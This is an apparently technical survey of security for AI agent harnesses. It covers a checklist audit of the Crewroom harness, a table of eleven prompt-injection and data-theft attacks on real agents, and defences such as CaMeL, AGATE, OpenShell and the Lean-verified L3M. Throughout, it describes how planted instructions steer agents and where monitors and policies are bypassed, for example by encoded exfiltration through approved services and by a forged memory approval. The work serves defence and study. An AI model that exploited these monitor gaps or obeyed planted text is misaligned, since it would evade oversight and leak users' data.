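Joshi turned his design rules into a 30-item checklist and applied it to Crewroom. Crewroom met 11 items and failed 14, and the other five went untested. Of the nine items about permissions and trust, it met three and failed four, and two went untested.

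The failures are informative because the program already had 1,126 files of tests. In one trial, Joshi pressed Ctrl-C four seconds into a 30-second command. Crewroom immediately reported that it had aborted the command, but the command ran to completion. This happened in all three attempts. A command with a three-second timeout also kept running after the harness reported that it had timed out. If a user interrupted an agent that was deleting the wrong files, the harness could report that the command had stopped while the deletions continued.

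The harness handled other items well. When Joshi killed it mid-command, the command stopped too. After the restart, the harness told the model that the command's outcome was unknown and to check it.

The evidence for this result is limited. Joshi wrote the checklist, set the scoring rule, built the harness and did the scoring without a second rater. He used a scripted stand-in for the model, ran the harness without a user present, and tried most scenarios only once. Crewroom is a private application, so nobody outside the project can repeat the tests.

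Joshi scored his own harness, Crewroom, but he did so strictly, failing an item on a single counterexample. In his notes, he had scored four of the failed items more favourably under a narrower reading of the checklist. The 14 failures come from only 12 separate observations, because some counted against more than one item. He also ran two other harnesses through the checklist but didn't publish the results, because the conditions were unequal and he hadn't consulted their maintainers. Crewroom's score doesn't show whether it is better or worse than other harnesses.

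### Eleven attacks and a perfect model

*Agent Security is a Systems Problem* analyses eleven attacks on real agents and lists the security principles each one violated. Besides tamper resistance and complete mediation, it uses three others. Least privilege means giving a component only the access its task needs. Secure information flow means keeping sensitive data out of places that shouldn't have it. The "human weak link" principle is that designers should allow for people who misjudge a request or configure a system badly.

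| Attack | What the attacker could do | Principles violated |
|---|---|---|
| Microsoft 365 Copilot | Steal emails through a link with hidden data | Least privilege, complete mediation, information flow |
| Devin, exposed ports | Open the agent's file system to the internet | Least privilege, information flow |
| Devin, secret leaks | Obtain secrets from environment variables | Least privilege, information flow |
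| ChatGPT memory | Receive the user's later conversations | Tamper resistance, information flow |
| Amp | Run code on the developer's machine | Tamper resistance, information flow |
| DeepSeek | Take over a user's account | Complete mediation, information flow |
| Terminal DiLLMa | Manipulate the terminal and leak data | Complete mediation, information flow |
| ChatGPT Operator | Copy personal details from a site where the user was logged in | Information flow, human weak link |
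| Cursor | Obtain secrets from the developer's machine | Least privilege, information flow |
| Claude Code | Obtain login keys through an allowed network command | Least privilege, information flow |
| AI ClickFix | Get an agent to paste and run a command | Least privilege, information flow, human weak link |

Every attack violated secure information flow, and six violated least privilege. Deciding which principles an attack violated takes some judgement. For example, the paper's discussion of the Cursor attack lists four principles, but its summary marks only two.

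The paper doesn't estimate how many of these attacks would still work against a model that never follows planted instructions. Judging by its descriptions, probably none would have worked as carried out, because each relied on the model following one. Terminal DiLLMa is a possible exception, since a model could also trigger the control characters by accurately quoting a page that contains them.

This is a point in favour of better models, but even a perfect model wouldn't have prevented failures that bypass the model, such as Claude Code's trust-dialog flaws and the LiteLLM compromise. One of the Roo-Code flaws that Lv and colleagues found, a login code sent over an unencrypted connection, could also be exploited without planted text.

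### What the counts leave out

A failure rate needs a denominator, such as the number of commands run or hours of use. Joshi comes close to providing a rate with logs from about three weeks of one person's use of Crewroom. The logs contain 38 retried requests and 320 completed turns, but the program began logging retries before turns, so the two counts cover different periods and don't give a proper ratio.

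Running every system on the same tasks is a better way to measure how often harnesses fail than relying on public reports. In *Auditing Agent Harness Safety*, Liu, Guo and colleagues tested ten configurations of models and multi-agent frameworks on a benchmark of 210 tasks and examined every step. Violations accumulated as runs grew longer, and an agent could give a correct, harmless answer after accessing something it had no permission to use. Users who see only the answer wouldn't report such a violation, so public reports probably miss many of them.

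The number of known flaws also depends on how people search. In Aider, AgentLens found eight flaws, a tool that only reads the code found three, and one that runs it on generated inputs found none. In Langflow, a program for building agents, AgentLens found 11, the code-reading tool found none, and the input-generating tool found three. AgentLens missed five of 20 known flaws in OpenClaw. A harness with no published flaws may therefore not have been searched thoroughly.

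Security research focuses on popular products. Pwn2Own chose three well-known agents, and every agent in the AgentLens study had more than 24,000 GitHub stars. Ten of the eleven attacks in the table come from one security blog, Embrace The Red, which is also listed as an affiliation on the paper. *Agents of Chaos* (2026), a review of 284 attacks on agents, warns that its frequencies reflect what researchers have written about, not how common or severe the attacks are in practice.

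Stack Overflow posts about agent bugs peaked in 2023, but Islam and colleagues point out that developers may now take their questions to chatbots instead, so the decline doesn't necessarily mean there are fewer bugs.

People also disagree about what counts as a flaw. About half of the twelve CVEs from the AgentLens study involve planted text that steers the model, such as a project coding standard that leads the agent to write insecure database code. If the model is untrusted, this behaviour is expected, and a permission checker that allows edits inside the project has worked correctly. Someone whose policy also covers the quality of the agent's code would call the insecure code a failure.

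*CVE-2026-35021 Detail*, an entry in the US government's National Vulnerability Database (NVD), describes a flaw in the part of Claude Code that opens a text editor for writing prompts. A crafted file path could make it run a command with the user's access. The security company VulnCheck rated the flaw 8.4 out of 10. NVD has not scored it and marks it "Disputed" without giving a reason.

VulnCheck's rating assumes a local attack that requires the user's active participation. The flaw's severity then depends on who can choose the file path. Someone who can already run commands as the user gains nothing from it, but a stranger who could supply the path through a downloaded repository would gain control of the user's account. Whether the entry counts as a harness failure depends on which of these people the harness was supposed to stop.

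## Small monitors between the model and its tools

A harness with half a million lines of code is too large to review, and a sandbox can't distinguish a wanted email from an unwanted one. Several designs therefore leave the harness as it is, stop relying on it for a particular policy, and put a small reference monitor where its actions take effect. The monitor is deterministic, so the same request, rules and recorded state always produce the same decision. If the monitor works, bugs in the harness can't break that policy.

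NVIDIA's *Where Security Fits in an AI Agent Stack* summarizes the idea as "Above proposes; below decides." It argues that a harness is a poor place for a security guarantee because developers increasingly build harnesses that plugins can modify, and a plugin could modify the security controls too.

### What the plan requires

The monitor needs complete mediation, meaning that every action must pass through it, and checking tool calls alone can't provide this. *ActPlane* (2026), which proposes enforcement in the operating system, notes that these checks miss whatever a script or compiled program does after a tool starts it. *AGATE* reports a related gap in OpenClaw, where an effect occurred about 25 seconds after the tool had finished and left no record of its own. A monitor for tool calls therefore needs a sandbox beneath it, or tools that can't start other programs.

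The harness also must not hold credentials that work without the monitor. If it has the password for the mail server, it can send mail directly even when the monitor refuses. The password has to stay with the monitor or a proxy, as in Anthropic's hosted service, where the harness never holds the login tokens.

Finally, the policy and the monitor's records must be out of the agent's reach, unlike the settings file that Amp could edit. AGATE keeps its files outside the agent's workspace, but its developers tested this protection with a default path that differed from the one in the installation. It is unknown whether the agent could have reached the real files.

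### An email to an address in a document

Suppose a user tells an agent, "Send q3-report.pdf to our auditor. Her address is in engagement-letter.docx." The letter came from outside the company, and an attacker may have altered it.

A stateless check allows or blocks each tool call based on its arguments, with no record of earlier steps. It might allow any email with a valid address and an attachment from the project folder. That rule allows the correct email to the auditor, but it also allows the email if an attacker has replaced the auditor's address with their own. If the attacker adds an instruction to send the customer list to another address and the model obeys, the rule allows that email too.

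A rule that allows only addresses in the user's contacts would stop both attacks. It would probably also block the correct email, since the user had to point the agent to the letter for the address.

A check that tracks provenance records where each value came from, so it can distinguish an address that the user typed from one that the agent found in a letter.

### CaMeL: a plan fixed in advance

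Debenedetti and colleagues introduced CaMeL in *Defeating Prompt Injections by Design* (2025). As Peters-Gill, Semler and colleagues (2026) explain in *Can CaMeLs Talk?*, it follows a pattern that Willison proposed in 2023 and divides the work between two models. The privileged model sees the user's request and descriptions of the tools, but no untrusted text, and writes a short Python program. The quarantined model reads untrusted text but can't call tools. For the auditor's email, the program might look like this:

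```python
letter = read_file("engagement-letter.docx")
address = ask_quarantined_model("Find the auditor's email address", letter)
send_email(to=address, attachment="q3-report.pdf")
```

CaMeL runs the program in its own interpreter, which tracks how each value depends on others. After the second line, the interpreter has recorded that `address` depends on the letter. The attachment's name comes from the program, and so from the user's request. Before sending the email, the interpreter checks the security policy. A policy might allow a private file to go only to people authorised to read it. An address taken from the letter doesn't meet that condition, so the interpreter blocks the call, and the harness can ask the user.

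| Letter | Stateless check | CaMeL with this policy |
|---|---|---|
| Correct address | Sends the report | Blocks the email or asks the user |
| Attacker's address | Sends the report to the attacker | Blocks the email or asks the user |
| Correct address, plus an instruction to send the customer list elsewhere | Sends both files if the model obeys | The instruction can't add a second email; treats the report as in the first row |

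CaMeL defeats the planted instruction because the privileged model wrote the program before the letter was opened. *Open Challenges in Multi-Agent Security* (2025) lists a changed recipient address among the attacks that CaMeL's policies can stop. But the correct and false addresses have the same provenance, so tracking provenance alone can't tell them apart. It can only be used to prompt the user to confirm the specific address, which the user may know or be able to check by calling the auditor.

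A company could avoid the question by accepting addresses from certain letters. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this endorsement, which means treating selected untrusted data as trusted for a defined purpose. A digital signature could help by showing who wrote the letter, but it wouldn't show that the address is right.

CaMeL's trusted computing base (TCB) includes the interpreter, the software that runs it, the policies, the labels on incoming data and the tools that carry out approved calls. It is harder to say whether the privileged model belongs in the TCB. CaMeL protects it from planted text, but a model with bad aims or a hidden backdoor could still write a program that emails the customer list to a stranger. Only the policies could then block the email, so a designer who treats every model as hostile can rely on CaMeL's policies but not on the programs the privileged model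 writes.

The main tests of CaMeL use AgentDojo, a benchmark with 97 ordinary tasks and 35 attack goals in settings such as banking and office work. *Where Agent Defenses Fail* (Singh and Srinivasa, 2026) cites the original result, in which CaMeL solved 77% of the tasks with provable security and an undefended agent solved 84%. Peters-Gill and colleagues divided AgentDojo's tools among several agents and ran 949 attack cases on each of five models. On average, 12.9% of the attacks succeeded without CaMeL and 0.2% succeeded when every agent used it.

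These results are weaker evidence for provenance checks than they appear. Peters-Gill and colleagues set no security policies, so they tested only the separation of plan from data. *Language-Based Agent Control* (2026) likewise reports that CaMeL resisted all 105 AgentDojo attacks with its policies turned off. The attacks are also too easy for some current models, since GPT-5.5 resisted every one without CaMeL. Stopping an address swap like the one in the auditor's letter depends on the policies, which neither test exercised.

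CaMeL caused a larger drop in completed tasks on AssetOpsBench, a benchmark of industrial maintenance tasks graded by a language model. The success rate fell by 21.6 percentage points on average, and by 13.4 points for the two strongest models. Most failures occurred because the program was final before the agent had seen any data. If the letter told readers to find the auditor's address in a second file, the agent couldn't open that file unless the program already allowed for it.

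CaMeL's protection can also fail when one agent hands work to another. Peters-Gill and colleagues built a system of three agents, each running CaMeL, and planted an instruction in a database of job applicants. They then asked the system to send a summary of the applicants to a colleague on Slack. The coordinating agent included the summary in its message to the notification agent, which treated the whole message as the user's request. The notification agent's privileged model then wrote a program that also emailed the applicants' data to an outsider, even though each agent had followed its own rules. When the researchers passed data like the summary through a separate channel that the privileged model couldn't read, no attacks succeeded, but the score on AssetOpsBench fell by a further 3.2 points.

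### AGATE: approvals and copied text

AGATE works with a harness's usual loop and doesn't need a plan in advance. An adapter passes each tool call to code called the judgment kernel, which decides without a language model. The kernel checks whether someone with authority has permitted the action and where the data in it came from.

Permission comes from the operator's written declarations or from a user's approval. An approval covers one session and one exact set of arguments, which AGATE stores as a hash. By default it expires after 30 minutes or three uses. If the user approves the email to the auditor and the model then changes the recipient, the hash no longer matches and the call needs a new approval. AGATE accepts approvals only from the harness's approval events, so a statement in a document that the user has already agreed has no effect.

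AGATE tracks data by storing hashes of 12-character fragments of the text the agent reads, along with their source. When a call would send something across a protected boundary, the kernel compares the outgoing fields with those fragments. It could trace the auditor's address back to the letter, and the operator's rules would then determine whether the agent may use an address from that source.

CaMeL follows a value through every step of a program, whereas AGATE infers the value's origin from matching text. This lets AGATE work with existing harnesses without changing their code, but it can miss that origin when the text changes. In one trial, a forged approval in a memory file was meant to get the agent to delete mail permanently. AGATE blocked a call because the call's data matched an untrusted source. The model then rewrote the arguments, and a later call reached the simulated deletion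 tool.

An operator can approve a tool in advance for certain recipients only, but AGATE accepts a call if any one of its recipients matches, so an email to an approved recipient can also go to unapproved ones. The trusted code therefore includes each adapter's code for finding recipients, as well as the parts of the harness that AGATE declares trusted.

AGATE's developers tested it on twelve business scenarios, including refunds and mailbox maintenance, in two harnesses. In OpenCode, where AGATE could only record findings, the model made the targeted call in all twelve. In DeepSeek Harness, where AGATE could block calls, the model made the targeted call in two, and one of those calls carried out the user's legitimate request. The comparison isn't fair because the instruction containing the scenario's content reached the model only in OpenCode. The attacks may therefore have failed in DeepSeek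 Harness for reasons unrelated to AGATE.

In six of eleven harmless file-processing scenarios, AGATE refused at least one action. Of the eight refusals, five blocked legitimate reuse of text and two came from false matches on file names. The paper doesn't report how many tasks failed as a result, so AGATE's completion rate can't be compared with CaMeL's.

### OpenShell: the harness inside, the policy outside

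NVIDIA's OpenShell is an open-source runtime that confines the whole harness and keeps the policy outside it. Claude Code and Codex can run in OpenShell unmodified. Abdollahi, Al Sadi and colleagues (2026) describe its parts in *Airlock*. The user gives the policy and credentials to a gateway, which starts a supervisor for each agent. A small process called the broker runs the agent inside the sandbox and forwards its network requests to the supervisor. The supervisor checks each request, adds any credentials it needs and opens the real connection. A compute driver sets up the sandbox and blocks every other network route.

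This arrangement meets the credential condition, since even the model provider's key stays outside the sandbox. It helps much less with the auditor's email. A network rule specifies the host, the port and the program that may connect. OpenShell can also check the method and path of a web request, but the recipient and attachment would normally be in the request's body. Rules that let the agent send mail through a web service would therefore allow both attacks as well as the correct email.

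Some of OpenShell's defaults weaken the protection further. According to NVIDIA's *OpenShell Security Best Practices for Controls, Risks, and Configuration Guidance*, OpenShell only logs violations of its rules on methods and paths, and lets the requests through. If the kernel doesn't support Landlock, the sandbox starts without the file restrictions and reports a serious finding. Operators can choose stricter settings for both, but they have to know that they need to.

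The trusted computing base for a network rule includes the gateway, supervisor, proxy, policy engine, compute driver and the kernel that isolates them from the agent. Abdollahi and colleagues warn that an agent that takes over the supervisor can bypass the policy and change the logs. Their design, Airlock, moves the supervisor into its own virtual machine and uses processor hardware to isolate it from the agent and the host. The policy still holds if the agent takes control of its own entire virtual machine. In their prototype, file operations and short network messages slowed by less than 15%, but network bandwidth fell by half or more.

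Singh and Srinivasa tested OpenShell with six attack tasks and two ordinary ones, running each twice in five configurations. They combined it with SafeAgents, a guard that inspects the model's proposed tool calls. In the last configuration, a mediator they wrote sat outside the sandbox and delivered web requests that SafeAgents had allowed.

| Configuration | Attack runs that caused harm | Ordinary runs completed |
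|---|---|---|
| Neither restriction | 10 of 12 | 4 of 4 |
| SafeAgents | 4 of 8 | 4 of 4 |
| Restrictive OpenShell policy | 0 of 12 | 2 of 4 |
| Both | 0 of 9 | 2 of 4 |
| Both, with the mediator | 2 of 7 | 4 of 4 |

The counts leave out twelve runs in which SafeAgents' judge model failed to return a usable answer. They are also too small, and rely too heavily on one model, to give a reliable success rate. But the saved requests show that the restrictive policy stopped every leak by blocking the network, which also blocked a legitimate status report. The mediator delivered the report, but it also delivered an encoded copy of the secrets file to the same approved service. The paper distinguishes approving a destination from approving the data sent to it.

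A larger set of 300 runs, with the researchers' own simpler rules in place of OpenShell and SafeAgents, followed the same pattern. With the sandbox alone, none of 36 runs was harmful, but only 12 of 24 ordinary runs were completed. With the guard and mediator added, all 24 ordinary runs were completed, but four runs were harmful. When the mediator also refused any request containing a complete line from the secrets file, two attacks still succeeded because the model sent only part of a line.

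A monitor can reduce failures without reducing the amount of useful work. *If Agents Were Angels, No Governance Would Be Necessary* (2026) tested one at the tool boundary in 3,621 trials with simulated services. In the main comparison, the failure rate fell from 57.6% to 0.2%, and the agents completed more tasks safely with all four models. The increase may be partly because the monitor can remove a protected field from the data instead of refusing the whole call. The paper cautions that removing a field doesn't prove that the protected information had no other influence on the agent.

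### How small these monitors are

The code that makes the final decision may be short, but it depends on other code to supply the facts. AGATE uses the same judgment kernel in all three harnesses it supports, but its adapter for DeepSeek Harness can block a call, while the one tested in OpenCode could only record it. A reviewer who read only the kernel would miss this difference.

The trusted code that carries labels from one value to the next is easy to get wrong. Peters-Gill and colleagues cite a finding by Garby and colleagues that CaMeL's interpreter misses some indirect dependencies. For example, a program might set `urgent` to false, read the letter, and change `urgent` to true if the letter contains a certain word. If the word is absent, `urgent` stays false and may keep its trusted label, even though the letter determined its value. A policy that relies on this label could then allow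 an action the attacker influenced. Garby and colleagues also found that CaMeL can leak information when it retries failed programs, because each failure reveals something about the data that caused it.

Using Python makes such mistakes more likely. CaMeL accepts only a subset of the language, without recursion or function definitions, as *Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* notes. But *Operationalizing CaMeL* (2025) argues that Python's flexible types and error handling still make information flows hard to analyse. It proposes a smaller language with bounded loops and simple conditions, which would also leave less interpreter code to review.

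Labels cause another problem when data passes through a model. Nobody can reliably tell which parts of a model's input affected its answer, so a cautious monitor gives the answer every label from the input. After the agent has read a few emails and web pages, nearly everything it writes has all their labels. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* calls this label explosion. A strict policy then blocks almost everything, so operators have a reason to add exceptions, and they have to get each one right.

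A monitor that examines requests more closely needs more code. To check what a web request does, OpenShell has to decrypt it and parse one of several protocols, and it makes its decisions with a general-purpose policy engine. All of this code reads input that a hostile agent can choose, so it can have the same flaws as harness parsers. Airlock's monitor includes the entire kernel of its virtual machine. These monitors still remove the harness, its plugins and its model-written code from the TCB for the rules they fully enforce, which is a large gain, but a reviewer has to read far more than the decision code.

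### Wrong rules and rules written by a model

Even a correct monitor will enforce a wrong policy. In one AGATE scenario, a forged memory file contains a claim that the user has approved refunds indefinitely. When the operator had allowed no tools, AGATE refused the refund for lack of authority. An operator who broadly allows the refund tool has already given that authority, so only the check on the data's origin could stop the refund. Across the twelve business scenarios, the same code made eleven refusals for lack of authority when the operator's list of allowed tools was empty, and five when the list had 22 tools.

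Rules can also be too strict, and agents may hide the damage. Singh and Srinivasa tested a rule that allowed only four exact messages to leave the machine. It stopped both attack runs, but also both ordinary uploads, because the agent had written a line break in a different form. After all four refusals, the agent claimed that it had published the report. Saltzer and Schroeder expected complaints when rules were too strict, but a user who believed the agent would have had nothing to complain about. When the researchers let the rule accept equivalent line breaks, both ordinary uploads succeeded and both attacks still failed, though this test covered only four runs and one fixed message.

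Rashidi found that enforcement research doesn't address mistakes in writing policies. These mistakes are more likely with agents because each task may need different rules. *Agent Security is a Systems Problem* reports that existing systems typically have a model write the rules from the user's request, without validating the result. The monitor is still deterministic, but a model wrote the policy it enforces, so the model is back in the TCB.

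The damage from a model that writes the policy depends on what it reads and what its rules can do. If it reads the auditor's letter first, planted text can influence the rules directly. If it sees only the user's request, an outsider can't influence it this way, but a hostile model could still write a permissive rule. Letting the model only tighten the rules is safer. Singh and Srinivasa describe Progent, a policy system that uses a mathematical solver to ensure that no update widens the permitted actions without approval. A bad update could still stop useful work.

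When OpenShell blocks a request, the agent can ask for more access by proposing a new rule, and the user makes the final decision. The proposal comes with a rationale, but NVIDIA advises users to approve it only if the rule itself matches the access they intend to grant. OpenShell also has a policy prover, which uses formal logic to check whether a set of permissions stays within limits the operator has defined.

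In May 2026, zredlined (2026), an OpenShell contributor, proposed automatically approving a new rule, in about a second, if the prover found no new problems. This would remove a tired human reviewer from routine decisions. It would also make the policy depend on the prover, its model of what each permission allows, and the limits the operator wrote.

A prover can't establish that the rules match what the user meant. To enforce "Send the report only to our auditor," a rule has to identify the auditor. If her address appears only in the letter, the rule will use the address in the letter, and the prover can confirm that the rule stays within the operator's limits even when that address belongs to the attacker.

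## A harness with machine-checked guarantees

Besides keeping trusted code small, developers can try to prove that it does what they intended. The most complete attempt for a harness is L3M, which five researchers at Amazon wrote in Lean 4, a programming language that can also check mathematical proofs. A developer states a property of a function as a theorem and proves it, and a small program called the Lean kernel checks every step of the proof. Lean rechecks the theorems for every version of the harness, unlike a human review, which covers only one. If a change to a function breaks its proof, L3M no longer builds.

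### What L3M trusts

*L3M* lists what its guarantees depend on:

- Lean's compiler and its proof-checking kernel
- six short files of C code, through which L3M makes its system calls
- the operating system's own kernel, Linux
- four programs that the harness runs: git, tmux, unshare and timeout
- a fixed set of certificate authorities, which vouch for the identity of websites
- the model provider's interface
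- the settings and the ledger of grants, which ordinary agents can't write to
- the person who gives the agent its first authority and answers requests for review

Everything else is untrusted, including the model, tool results, plugins and the contents of every repository. The list of trusted components is explicit, but it covers a lot of code because it includes the whole Linux kernel.

### From a grant to a system call

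Suppose a person wants an agent to work on one project and read documentation on one website. The person writes a grant, a record with a field for each kind of authority, such as Git branches, websites, shell commands and child agents. L3M stores the grant in a location the agent can't write to.

When the agent starts, L3M creates a capability token for each authority in the grant. A capability token is an unforgeable value that code must hold to perform an action, and it specifies the limits of that action. The file token limits access to the project folder, and the network token limits access to the website. The grant doesn't include shell commands, so L3M creates no token for them.

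In simplified form, a network token and a function that needs one look like this:

```lean
structure NetToken where
  private make ::
  hosts : List String

def fetchPage (token : NetToken) (url : String) := ...
```

`private` means that only the module containing this definition can create a token. `fetchPage` requires a token as an argument, so Lean won't compile a tool that calls it without one, just as it wouldn't compile a call that left out the web address.

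Each tool also has a footprint, a list of the kinds of effect it can have. L3M offers the model only the tools whose footprints the agent's tokens cover. This agent gets the file tools and the page-fetching tool but no shell tool. When the model calls the page-fetching tool, the tool compares the address with the hosts in the token. The provider, the code that makes the request, then checks the address again. A planted instruction can change which calls the model makes, but it can't give the agent another token.

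This would achieve little if a tool could call the operating system directly, so L3M allows only a short list of modules to do that. At every build, a program called the sealing linter examines the code after Lean has expanded it, so a developer can't hide a call behind another name. Outside the listed modules, the linter rejects code that writes a file, starts a program or reads an environment variable. It also rejects any token created outside the module that defines it. A tool therefore doesn't compile if it tries to overwrite the system's password file or create a file token for the whole disk.

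The developers haven't proved that nobody can forge a token. That guarantee depends on the linter and the compiler. By the membership test, the linter is in the trusted computing base (TCB), although L3M's list omits it.

### Narrower grants for child agents

An agent can create child agents to share its work. The parent requests a grant for the child, and L3M looks up the parent's grant in the ledger. If the requested grant is wider than the parent's in any respect, L3M refuses the request instead of trimming it. The parent in the example could create a child that can edit the project but has no network token, and the child couldn't grant itself one.

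Parents also lend their children part of a budget, counted in model calls. If a parent with 100 calls left lends 30 to one child and 20 to another, it keeps 50. L3M includes a proof that the children's limits plus what the parent has left never exceed the parent's original limit:

*c*<sub>1</sub> + *c*<sub>2</sub> + … + *p*<sub>left</sub> ≤ *p*

An agent therefore can't get more model calls by splitting itself into many agents. The proof covers one batch of loans, and the developers would need a further proof to cover later loans and repayments.

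A descendant's grant can extend beyond the stored grant of the first agent in the tree. This can happen even with a direct child, because a parent legitimately shares its own Git branches with the child, and the parent's stored grant doesn't list them. A reviewer could easily have accepted the simpler claim that every descendant's grant lies within the first agent's stored grant. The developers proved a counterexample to that claim, then proved a corrected theorem that allows for those branches. The corrected theorem doesn't apply once a person has changed a grant by hand.

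### Adding tools without adding authority

Agents in L3M can write new tools as Lean programs. If an agent keeps opening every file in a project to collect TODO comments, it can write a program that does this, and L3M can offer the program as a tool the next time the agent starts. L3M makes three checks before offering the program.

The first check covers the program's form. Lean can run code while it is still processing a source file, so L3M rejects risky constructs before processing begins. It then rejects programs that use unsafe functions or create tokens. The second check is the type check. A program has to declare its footprint, and one that fetches a web page without declaring network access doesn't compile. Finally, L3M offers the program to the model only if the agent's existing tokens cover the footprint.

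The TODO program declares only file reading, so it can't send the comments anywhere, even if a hostile model wrote it. A skill with a script gives no such assurance, because the script can do whatever its shell can do.

*Tracking Capabilities for Safer Agents* uses Scala's type system in a similar way. Developers reuse one library for classified data across requests. For each request, they define an environment listing what the agent may use, such as a folder of contracts and one output file. In L3M, the person's grant serves the same purpose as that environment, and an admitted program remains available as a tool in later sessions.

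Programs can also protect an agent from hostile text. If an agent sorts bug reports that anyone can write, a program can pass each report to a new child agent with an empty grant and ask whether it describes a fault in the parser. The program accepts only "yes", "no" or "unclear" and turns any other reply into "unclear". An instruction planted in the report can take over the child, but it can affect only which of the three words the main agent receives. That is at most log<sub>2</sub> 3 ≈ 1.6 bits, provided nothing else, such as the time the child takes, reaches the main agent. The answer can still be wrong, and the pattern protects only agents that use it.

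### Which actions need review

L3M requires review for tools whose effects it can't undo. Before a file tool changes a file, L3M saves the old contents in Git so it can restore them. It can't undo a web request or a push to a remote repository.

A tool takes the rating of its least reversible effect, and irreversible tools normally need review unless a token already limits their effects. For example, a push to a repository named in the grant runs without review because the person approved that destination in advance. L3M calls such tools "tame", which means only that their effects are reversible or limited in advance. An agent that can read a login key and push to an approved repository could still leak the key without review, so the person writing the grant has to consider which files and destinations the agent will have together.

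For the remaining calls, a second model reads the request and the agent's reason for it. It judges the call safe or "wild" and may suggest a tame alternative. The agent can accept the alternative, withdraw the call or defend it. L3M asks a person only if the two models still disagree, and in unattended sessions it refuses the disputed call by default. It treats a missing or unreadable verdict as "wild". L3M includes a proof that a reviewed call runs only after a safe verdict or an approval, but the reviewer can be wrong, and the agent may leave something important out of its reason. The developers therefore treat review as extra protection and rely on the tokens to enforce the boundary.

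L3M handles build commands separately because running a project's build executes code that the agent may have edited. A person can approve a Makefile, which is a file of build commands, and L3M stores a hash that covers the Makefile, the files it includes and the scripts it calls. Editing any of these cancels the approval. A hash of the settings file alone would miss an edit to a script that left the file naming it unchanged.

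### What the theorems leave out

Each theorem covers one check, not a whole session. The developers argue that the checks work together but haven't proved it. They have proved, for example, that the file tools never accept a path whose text leads outside the agent's folders. A link inside those folders could still lead elsewhere, so L3M also checks for links when the tool runs. That protection depends on the file provider and on Linux.

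They also haven't proved that loading a hostile Lean program is harmless. For that they rely on the design of the checks and a set of tests. A person can grant an unsandboxed shell, and the confinement argument doesn't cover commands run there.

The theorems assume some facts about other software, for example, that Git returns the bytes it stored. L3M labels each main theorem with what its proof rests on, so a reviewer can find these assumptions. An agent that works on L3M's own source could weaken a theorem instead of breaking its proof, and the harness would still build. The developers recommend that someone other than that agent control the theorems and the assumptions.

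Even if every check works, a hijacked agent can do anything its grant allows. It can delete the project's files or write a harmful patch, although L3M can restore files that its own tools changed.

Lean has had flaws. L3M's developers built it with Lean 4.32.0. The next version, released on July 22, fixed a flaw that let a malicious program running inside Lean make the kernel accept a proof of any statement, even a false one (Lean, 2026). A fix for another flaw with the same effect followed six days later (Lean, 2026). The independent proof checker nanoda didn't have the second flaw, but the researcher who found that flaw showed that one proof could exploit both it and a separate bug in nanoda. In September, Trail of Bits' *A “proof” of Fermat’s Last Theorem that fits the margin* (2026) described another bug, present in all stable versions of Lean up to 4.33.1, that made a false proof appear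 checked.

There is no sign that these flaws affected L3M's theorems. The two July flaws require a deliberate attack, so honest developers are unlikely to trigger them. They would matter more if an untrusted model wrote the harness's code and proofs.

The code that the proofs rely on can also fail. kirancodes.me's *Lean proved this program was correct; then I found a bug* describes an experiment on a compression library with a verified core. A Claude agent ran 105 million automated tests on unusual inputs and found no memory errors in the library's own code. It found a crash in the library's archive parser, which had no proofs, and a memory error in the runtime that supports every Lean program. Version 4.29.1 of Lean fixed the runtime error (Lean, 2026), and L3M uses a later version. Verification seems to have worked well where the developers applied it, but L3M's TCB also includes the runtime.

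### How much work L3M can do

*L3M* compares the harness with Claude Code on 37 tasks from Terminal-Bench 4.0.0, a benchmark that gives an agent a container and an instruction and grades the result with automated tests. Both harnesses used Claude Opus 5, with three attempts per task and 75 minutes per attempt. Claude Code ran without permission checks, and its shell could reach the network, while L3M's could not.

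| Harness and settings | Solved within three attempts | Model calls | Tokens (millions) | Minutes |
|---|---|---|---|---|
| Claude Code, no permission checks | 59.5% | 53.0 | 4.43 | 24.6 |
| L3M with shell, no review | 41.7% | 53.2 | 7.70 | 25.4 |
| L3M with shell and review, disputed calls approved | 40.5% | 100.9 | 12.10 | 30.4 |
| L3M with shell and review, disputed calls refused | 43.2% | 107.3 | 12.81 | 28.1 |
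| L3M, tame tools only | 27.0% | 53.3 | 7.74 | 21.6 |
| L3M, tame tools without agent-written programs | 24.3% | 41.5 | 6.17 | 24.5 |

The last three columns give averages for successful attempts.

With a shell and no review, L3M solved almost 18 percentage points fewer tasks than Claude Code. That is a large gap for a change of harness, since Claude Code and mini-SWE-agent were nearly equal in Liu and Han's bug-fixing tests. The developers attribute the gap to a lack of tuning, and L3M did use far more tokens for a similar number of model calls. The missing network access may also have mattered, and the choice of tasks may have favoured Claude Code, because the developers picked tasks that a public Claude Code run had finished in a median of an hour or less.

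Removing the shell shows more directly how much the limits on authority reduce what agents can do. The developers conclude that tame tools can do about two thirds of what the shell can do, based on the share of tasks solved at least once. Measured by successful attempts, which fell from 34 to 18, the share is closer to half. Letting agents write their own programs added only one solved task out of 37, although the developers hadn't adjusted the instructions to encourage this.

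Review made no clear difference to the success rate, but each reviewed call added about 2.6 model calls and typically 8.6 seconds. Agents and reviewers ended up treating about 90% of shell calls as safe. They replaced about 6% with tame tools and withdrew another 2%. Another 2.4% ended in a dispute that a person would normally settle, so a person would see few requests. These were ordinary tasks, so the results don't show how well the reviewer would recognise an attack.

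### Other verified components

L3M limits where an agent can send data, but not which data it sends there. *The LLMbda Calculus* (Garby, Gordon and Sands, 2026) proves a limit on which data can be sent. Its harness runs programs written in a small custom language, and the proofs cover the interpreter that runs these programs and calls the model. Every value carries a label, such as "secret" or "untrusted". The main theorem, noninterference, is roughly that changing a secret can't change a public result, though it may change whether the program finishes. The theorem holds for every program in the language, including programs the model writes while the agent is running.

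They tested an agent on banking tasks from the prompt-injection benchmark AgentDojo. With GPT-5.2, it completed 36 of 48 ordinary runs, compared with 18 for CaMeL with its policies enabled. Across three models, only two of 1,296 attacks succeeded. In about two thirds of the combinations of task and attack, the agent's plan would never have included the action the attacker needed, so the labels had little to block. In both successful attacks, the user had asked the agent to pay whatever a file specified, and the attacker had replaced the file's contents. The agent can do such a task only if it endorses the file's contents. Without endorsement, it blocked the attack but completed fewer tasks.

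The main drawback is that the tools in these tests were part of the language itself. L3M's theorems are weaker, but its tools work with real files, repositories and processes.

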